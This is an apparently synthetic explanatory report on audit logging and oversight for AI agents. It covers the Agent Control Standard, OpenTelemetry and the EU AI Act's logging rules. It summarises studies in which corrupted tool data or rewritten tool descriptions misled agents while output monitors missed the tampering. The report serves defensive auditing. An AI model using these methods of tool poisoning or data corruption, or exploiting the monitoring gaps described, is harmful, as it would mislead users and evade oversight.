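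The Agent Control Standard (ACS) requires an agent's software to pause at fixed points, called hooks, and send a message to a separate program, the Guardian Agent. The Guardian replies with one of five decisions: allow, deny, modify, ask or defer. A May draft of version 0.1.0 requires hooks at the start and end of a session, when a request arrives, before each tool call, after each tool result, and when the agent gives its answer. Ticket 4812 involves three tool calls, so the Guardian would receive at least ten messages. The Guardian can use each message to block a step as well as record it, so ACS is both a policy layer and a logging standard.

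Every conforming system must implement this core, which includes a unique identifier and time on each message, and a chain of records in which each hash depends on the one before. If someone deletes record 40, the hashes from record 41 onwards no longer match. The draft leaves much of the sample record for ticket 4812 to optional profiles, which a company can add separately.

| Item | Required in the core? | Optional profile |
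|---|---|---|
| Messages for tool calls and results | Yes | – |
| Events in a standard log format | No | Trace |
| Inventory of models, tools and their versions | No | Inspect |
| Origin of each piece of data | No | Provenance |
| Hash of each message's full content | Recommended | Audit |
| Post-quantum digital signatures | No | Crypto |
| Hash of each tool definition | No | None |

A buyer who hears that a product "supports ACS" should ask which profiles it supports. Without the Audit profile, the chain may cover only facts about each step, such as its type and time. Someone with access to the log could then change the recorded recipient of an email without breaking the chain.

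The last row matters most for tool-call drift. The inventory lists a tool's name, version, supplier and general capability, such as deleting files. Another profile reports when a component appears, disappears or changes version during a session. If a server rewrites a tool's description but keeps the same version number, as Invariant Labs' WhatsApp server could have done, it might never trigger a report. A company that adopts ACS should add the definition hash.

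It may also have to wait for products. The roadmap on the Agent Control Standard's project page schedules working agent instrumentation and a sample Guardian for version 1, which follows the current preview. However, the launch announcement already mentioned open-source reference implementations.

### OpenTelemetry and Article 12 of the EU AI Act

Many companies already use OpenTelemetry, an open standard for recording how software runs, mostly to find faults and slow steps. It describes a task as a series of timed steps called spans. Its conventions for generative AI give suppliers common names for model calls and tool calls. In April 2026, OpenTelemetry's *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans* still had the status "Development", so the names could change.

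Under these conventions, the email to Mia would appear as a span called `execute_tool send_email`. Axiom, a company that stores such data, lists fields for the tool's arguments, the agent's identifier and the conversation, to be included "when available". Two suppliers can therefore both follow the conventions even if only one records who received the email. Greptime (2026), a database company, explains that OpenTelemetry's library for OpenAI's interface records prompts and answers only if the developer turns this on. A company that keeps the default will have the timing of every call but no copy of the hidden paragraph. Engineers also often keep only a sample of their traces to save money, which is reasonable for studying speed but useless if the sample leaves out the session that leaked.

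ACS and OpenTelemetry can work together, since the Trace profile can write its events in OpenTelemetry's format. Another proposal, *Agent Audit Trail* (Sharif, 2026), would require fields for the agent's identity, action type, outcome and trust level. It is one author's submission to the Internet Engineering Task Force, which sets many internet standards, and has no official standing so far.

European law will require logs for some AI systems, but in much more general terms. According to the European Commission's *Article 12*, high-risk AI systems must be able to record events automatically throughout their lifetime. These events must help identify risks and "substantial modification", and help monitor the system in use. The duty has not started, as an amendment postponed it. Cooley, a law firm, dates the amendment to 24 July 2026. artificialintelligenceact.eu's *Article 12* now gives start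 dates of 2 December 2027 for the uses listed in the act's Annex III and 2 August 2028 for systems under Annex I, which covers regulated products such as machinery.

Annex III includes AI used in employment, education, credit assessment, law enforcement and critical infrastructure, according to the National Law Review. An agent that screens job applications could fall under it, but an assistant that answers complaints about parcels probably doesn't. Even for systems that Annex III covers, Article 12 doesn't list the fields in the sample record. It sets minimum log contents only for remote biometric identification, such as matching faces against a database, and these include the times of use and the people who verified a match.

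The reference to substantial modification may be relevant to drift. The act uses the term for an unplanned change, made after a system goes on the market, that affects its compliance or intended purpose. A changed tool could qualify, so a provider of a high-risk agent has a reason to record tool versions as well as calls.

### When the log looks normal and the advice is bad

A complete log can still contain nothing that looks wrong. In *AgentDrift*, Wu, Koshiyama and colleagues (2026) replayed investment conversations from ten users, each with 23 requests for advice, on seven models. The agent ranked three to five investments using tools that returned market data and news. They ran each conversation once with the original data and once with corrupted data.

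The corruption reversed a five-point risk scale, so Tesla's shares were rated 1 (defensive) instead of 5 (speculative). It also changed figures such as volatility to match the false ratings, added misleading headlines, and presented a very risky fund as safe. The models, their instructions and the tools' names stayed the same.

Wu and colleagues first scored the advice with NDCG, a standard measure of rankings:

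DCG = Σ *rel*(*k*) / log₂(*k* + 1)  NDCG = DCG / IDCG

Here *rel*(*k*) is an expert's grade for the investment in position *k*, and IDCG is the highest possible DCG. The grades are the same for every user, so replacing Verizon with the riskier Amazon hardly changes the score, even if the user wants to avoid risk. A second version of the score gives no credit for investments above the user's risk limit. The table shows four of the models.

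| Model | Usual score, clean → corrupted | Safety-adjusted score, clean → corrupted | Turns with unsuitable advice, corrupted |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.2 | 0.728 → 0.727 | 0.443 → 0.333 | 88.3% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 0.744 → 0.723 | 0.467 → 0.290 | 92.6% |
| Gemma 3 12B | 0.651 → 0.707 | 0.383 → 0.218 | 87.4% |
| Qwen2.5-7B | 0.654 → 0.632 | 0.278 → 0.272 | 64.8% |

Across all seven models, at least one recommendation was too risky for the user in 65% to 93% of turns with corrupted data. The rate was already 46% to 78% with clean data, so the increase is smaller than the first figures suggest. The models had only ten shares to choose from, and a turn counted if even one recommended share was unsuitable. A later version of the study, *Sell Me This Stock*, covers eight models and reports a range of 65% to 99% with corrupted data.

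The audit log of one of these sessions would show that the right agent called an approved tool with sensible arguments, the policy layer allowed the call, and the tool reported success. The log would also contain Tesla's false risk score, but a reader would need the true score to notice the error. The agent's explanations would not help much, since 80% of the risk scores that agents cited repeated the corrupted value. In 1,563 corrupted turns, no agent explicitly questioned whether the data was reliable.

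Asking the agent to check its own advice failed too, because the check used the same corrupted data. In another test, a frontier model compared the data with what it already knew and flagged corruption in 99% to 100% of turns, but the advice was no more suitable overall. *Sell Me This Stock* recommends a check against a source the agent can't influence. For the support assistant, ordinary code could compare a promised delivery date with the parcel company's record before the email goes out.

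Agents cope better when only one result is wrong. *When Tool Outputs Go Wrong* falsified one important tool result while agents answered factual questions, then left the results of later calls unaltered. The agents still reached the correct answer in 87.5% of the judged runs. They mostly recovered without mentioning the false result, so a company that reads only final answers wouldn't learn that a tool had failed.

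Records of which software was running can reveal changes that the output does not. *Stronger Judges Do Not See More* (2026) compares checks of a system's output with a check of its identity across six kinds of tampering. In cases with an altered tool, four output checks accepted between 82.9% and 95.0%, and the identity check accepted none. A language model asked to flag suspicious output flagged 52.6% of cases with altered instructions, but also 54.0% of untouched ones. The identity check's perfect result is expected, since it only has to detect a difference from the approved system. It would probably have missed the corrupted investment data, because an approved tool can return false data without any change to its code.

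Even so, once someone discovers the corruption, the company can search the log for every session that received the false scores and contact the affected clients. It could not do this if it had kept only the final advice.

### Alerts on changed tool definitions

If the log includes tool definitions, software can compare each definition's hash with the approved one and alert the security team if they differ. But the clients that most employees use don't write the full tool list anywhere a security team can search, according to trackr.live, a small security blog. It recommends capturing the list in a gateway between the clients and the tool servers. A gateway can't capture definitions from a server that a developer runs on a laptop, because the traffic never crosses the network.

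Most alerts will come from legitimate changes, because suppliers edit their tools far more often than attackers do. If a company uses 200 tools and each definition changes three times a year, it will get 600 alerts a year, or about twelve a week. If an attacker changes one definition every two years, one alert in 1,200 comes from an attack. Grouping alerts by release reduces the work, since one update often changes several tools. A change with a new version number can wait in the queue for reapproval, but a change without one should alert someone at once.

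Tools under development also set off many alerts, because developers edit the descriptions all day. trackr.live calls this the most common reason that teams switch such alerts off in the second month, though it gives no figures. It advises logging development servers separately, with the alert disabled. It also suggests scanning changed descriptions for commands aimed at the model, and using a match only to make an existing alert more urgent. Legitimate descriptions mention files and keys too, so the scan alone would raise too many false alarms.

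### Evidence from real incidents

Public accounts of attacks seldom include an agent's logs, and no well-documented case from 2025 or 2026 shows a company using them to work out what an injected agent did for a real attacker. Outsiders have only the vendors' statements about EchoLeak and ForcedLeak. HiddenLayer reports that 31% of organisations can't tell whether they have had a breach involving an agent. It sells AI security and so benefits from such worries, but the figure is plausible if many logs resemble OWASP's samples.

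An agent's log may also not be enough by itself. It would have missed the blind copies that postmark-mcp sent, which only the mail service's delivery records would have shown. The message identifier in the sample record for ticket 4812 lets an investigator match the agent's log to those delivery records. A company should find out how long its mail service, database and other systems keep their records, and save copies if the period is short.

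### Personal data, storage and outages

The sample record contains Jonas's address, so anyone who can read the log can read it too. The company can reduce this risk by keeping the email's body and the ticket's text in a separate store, with fewer readers and an earlier deletion date. The log then holds only a reference and a hash. If the log's records are chained, this also lets the company delete the text at Jonas's request without breaking every later hash.

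After the deletion, the company can still show that an email went to Mia and who approved it. It can also confirm that a copy Mia hands over matches the hash, but it can't recover the text from the hash. Short values such as phone numbers need a hash that includes a secret key, because without the key anyone could try all the likely numbers until one matched. Passwords and access tokens should not reach the log, so software has to remove them before it writes the record.

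Deleting logs early has a drawback because hostile text can sit in a database for months before an employee asks the agent about it, as with ForcedLeak's sales leads. Providers of high-risk systems will have to keep the logs they control for at least six months, according to artificialintelligenceact.eu's *Article 19*.

Storage grows quickly if the company saves the model's whole input at every step, because the software resends the earlier text each time. A hypothetical task with 20 model calls might start with 40 kilobytes of instructions and tool definitions and add 5 kilobytes between calls. Saving every input in full takes 20 × 40 + 5 × (0 + 1 + … + 19) = 1,750 kilobytes, while saving each piece of text once takes 40 + 19 × 5 = 135 kilobytes. At 10,000 tasks a day, that is 1.35 gigabytes a day instead of 17.5. The instructions and tool definitions rarely change between tasks, so keeping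 one shared copy of them reduces storage further.

Recording a tool call does not stop it, but if the software saves the request before the tool acts and the result afterwards, a crash in between leaves a request without a result. The company then knows it must check whether, for example, an email went out. The company also has to decide what the assistant may do when the log is unavailable. It could let the assistant keep reading tickets but block `send_email` until logging works again, in which case customers wait for their replies.
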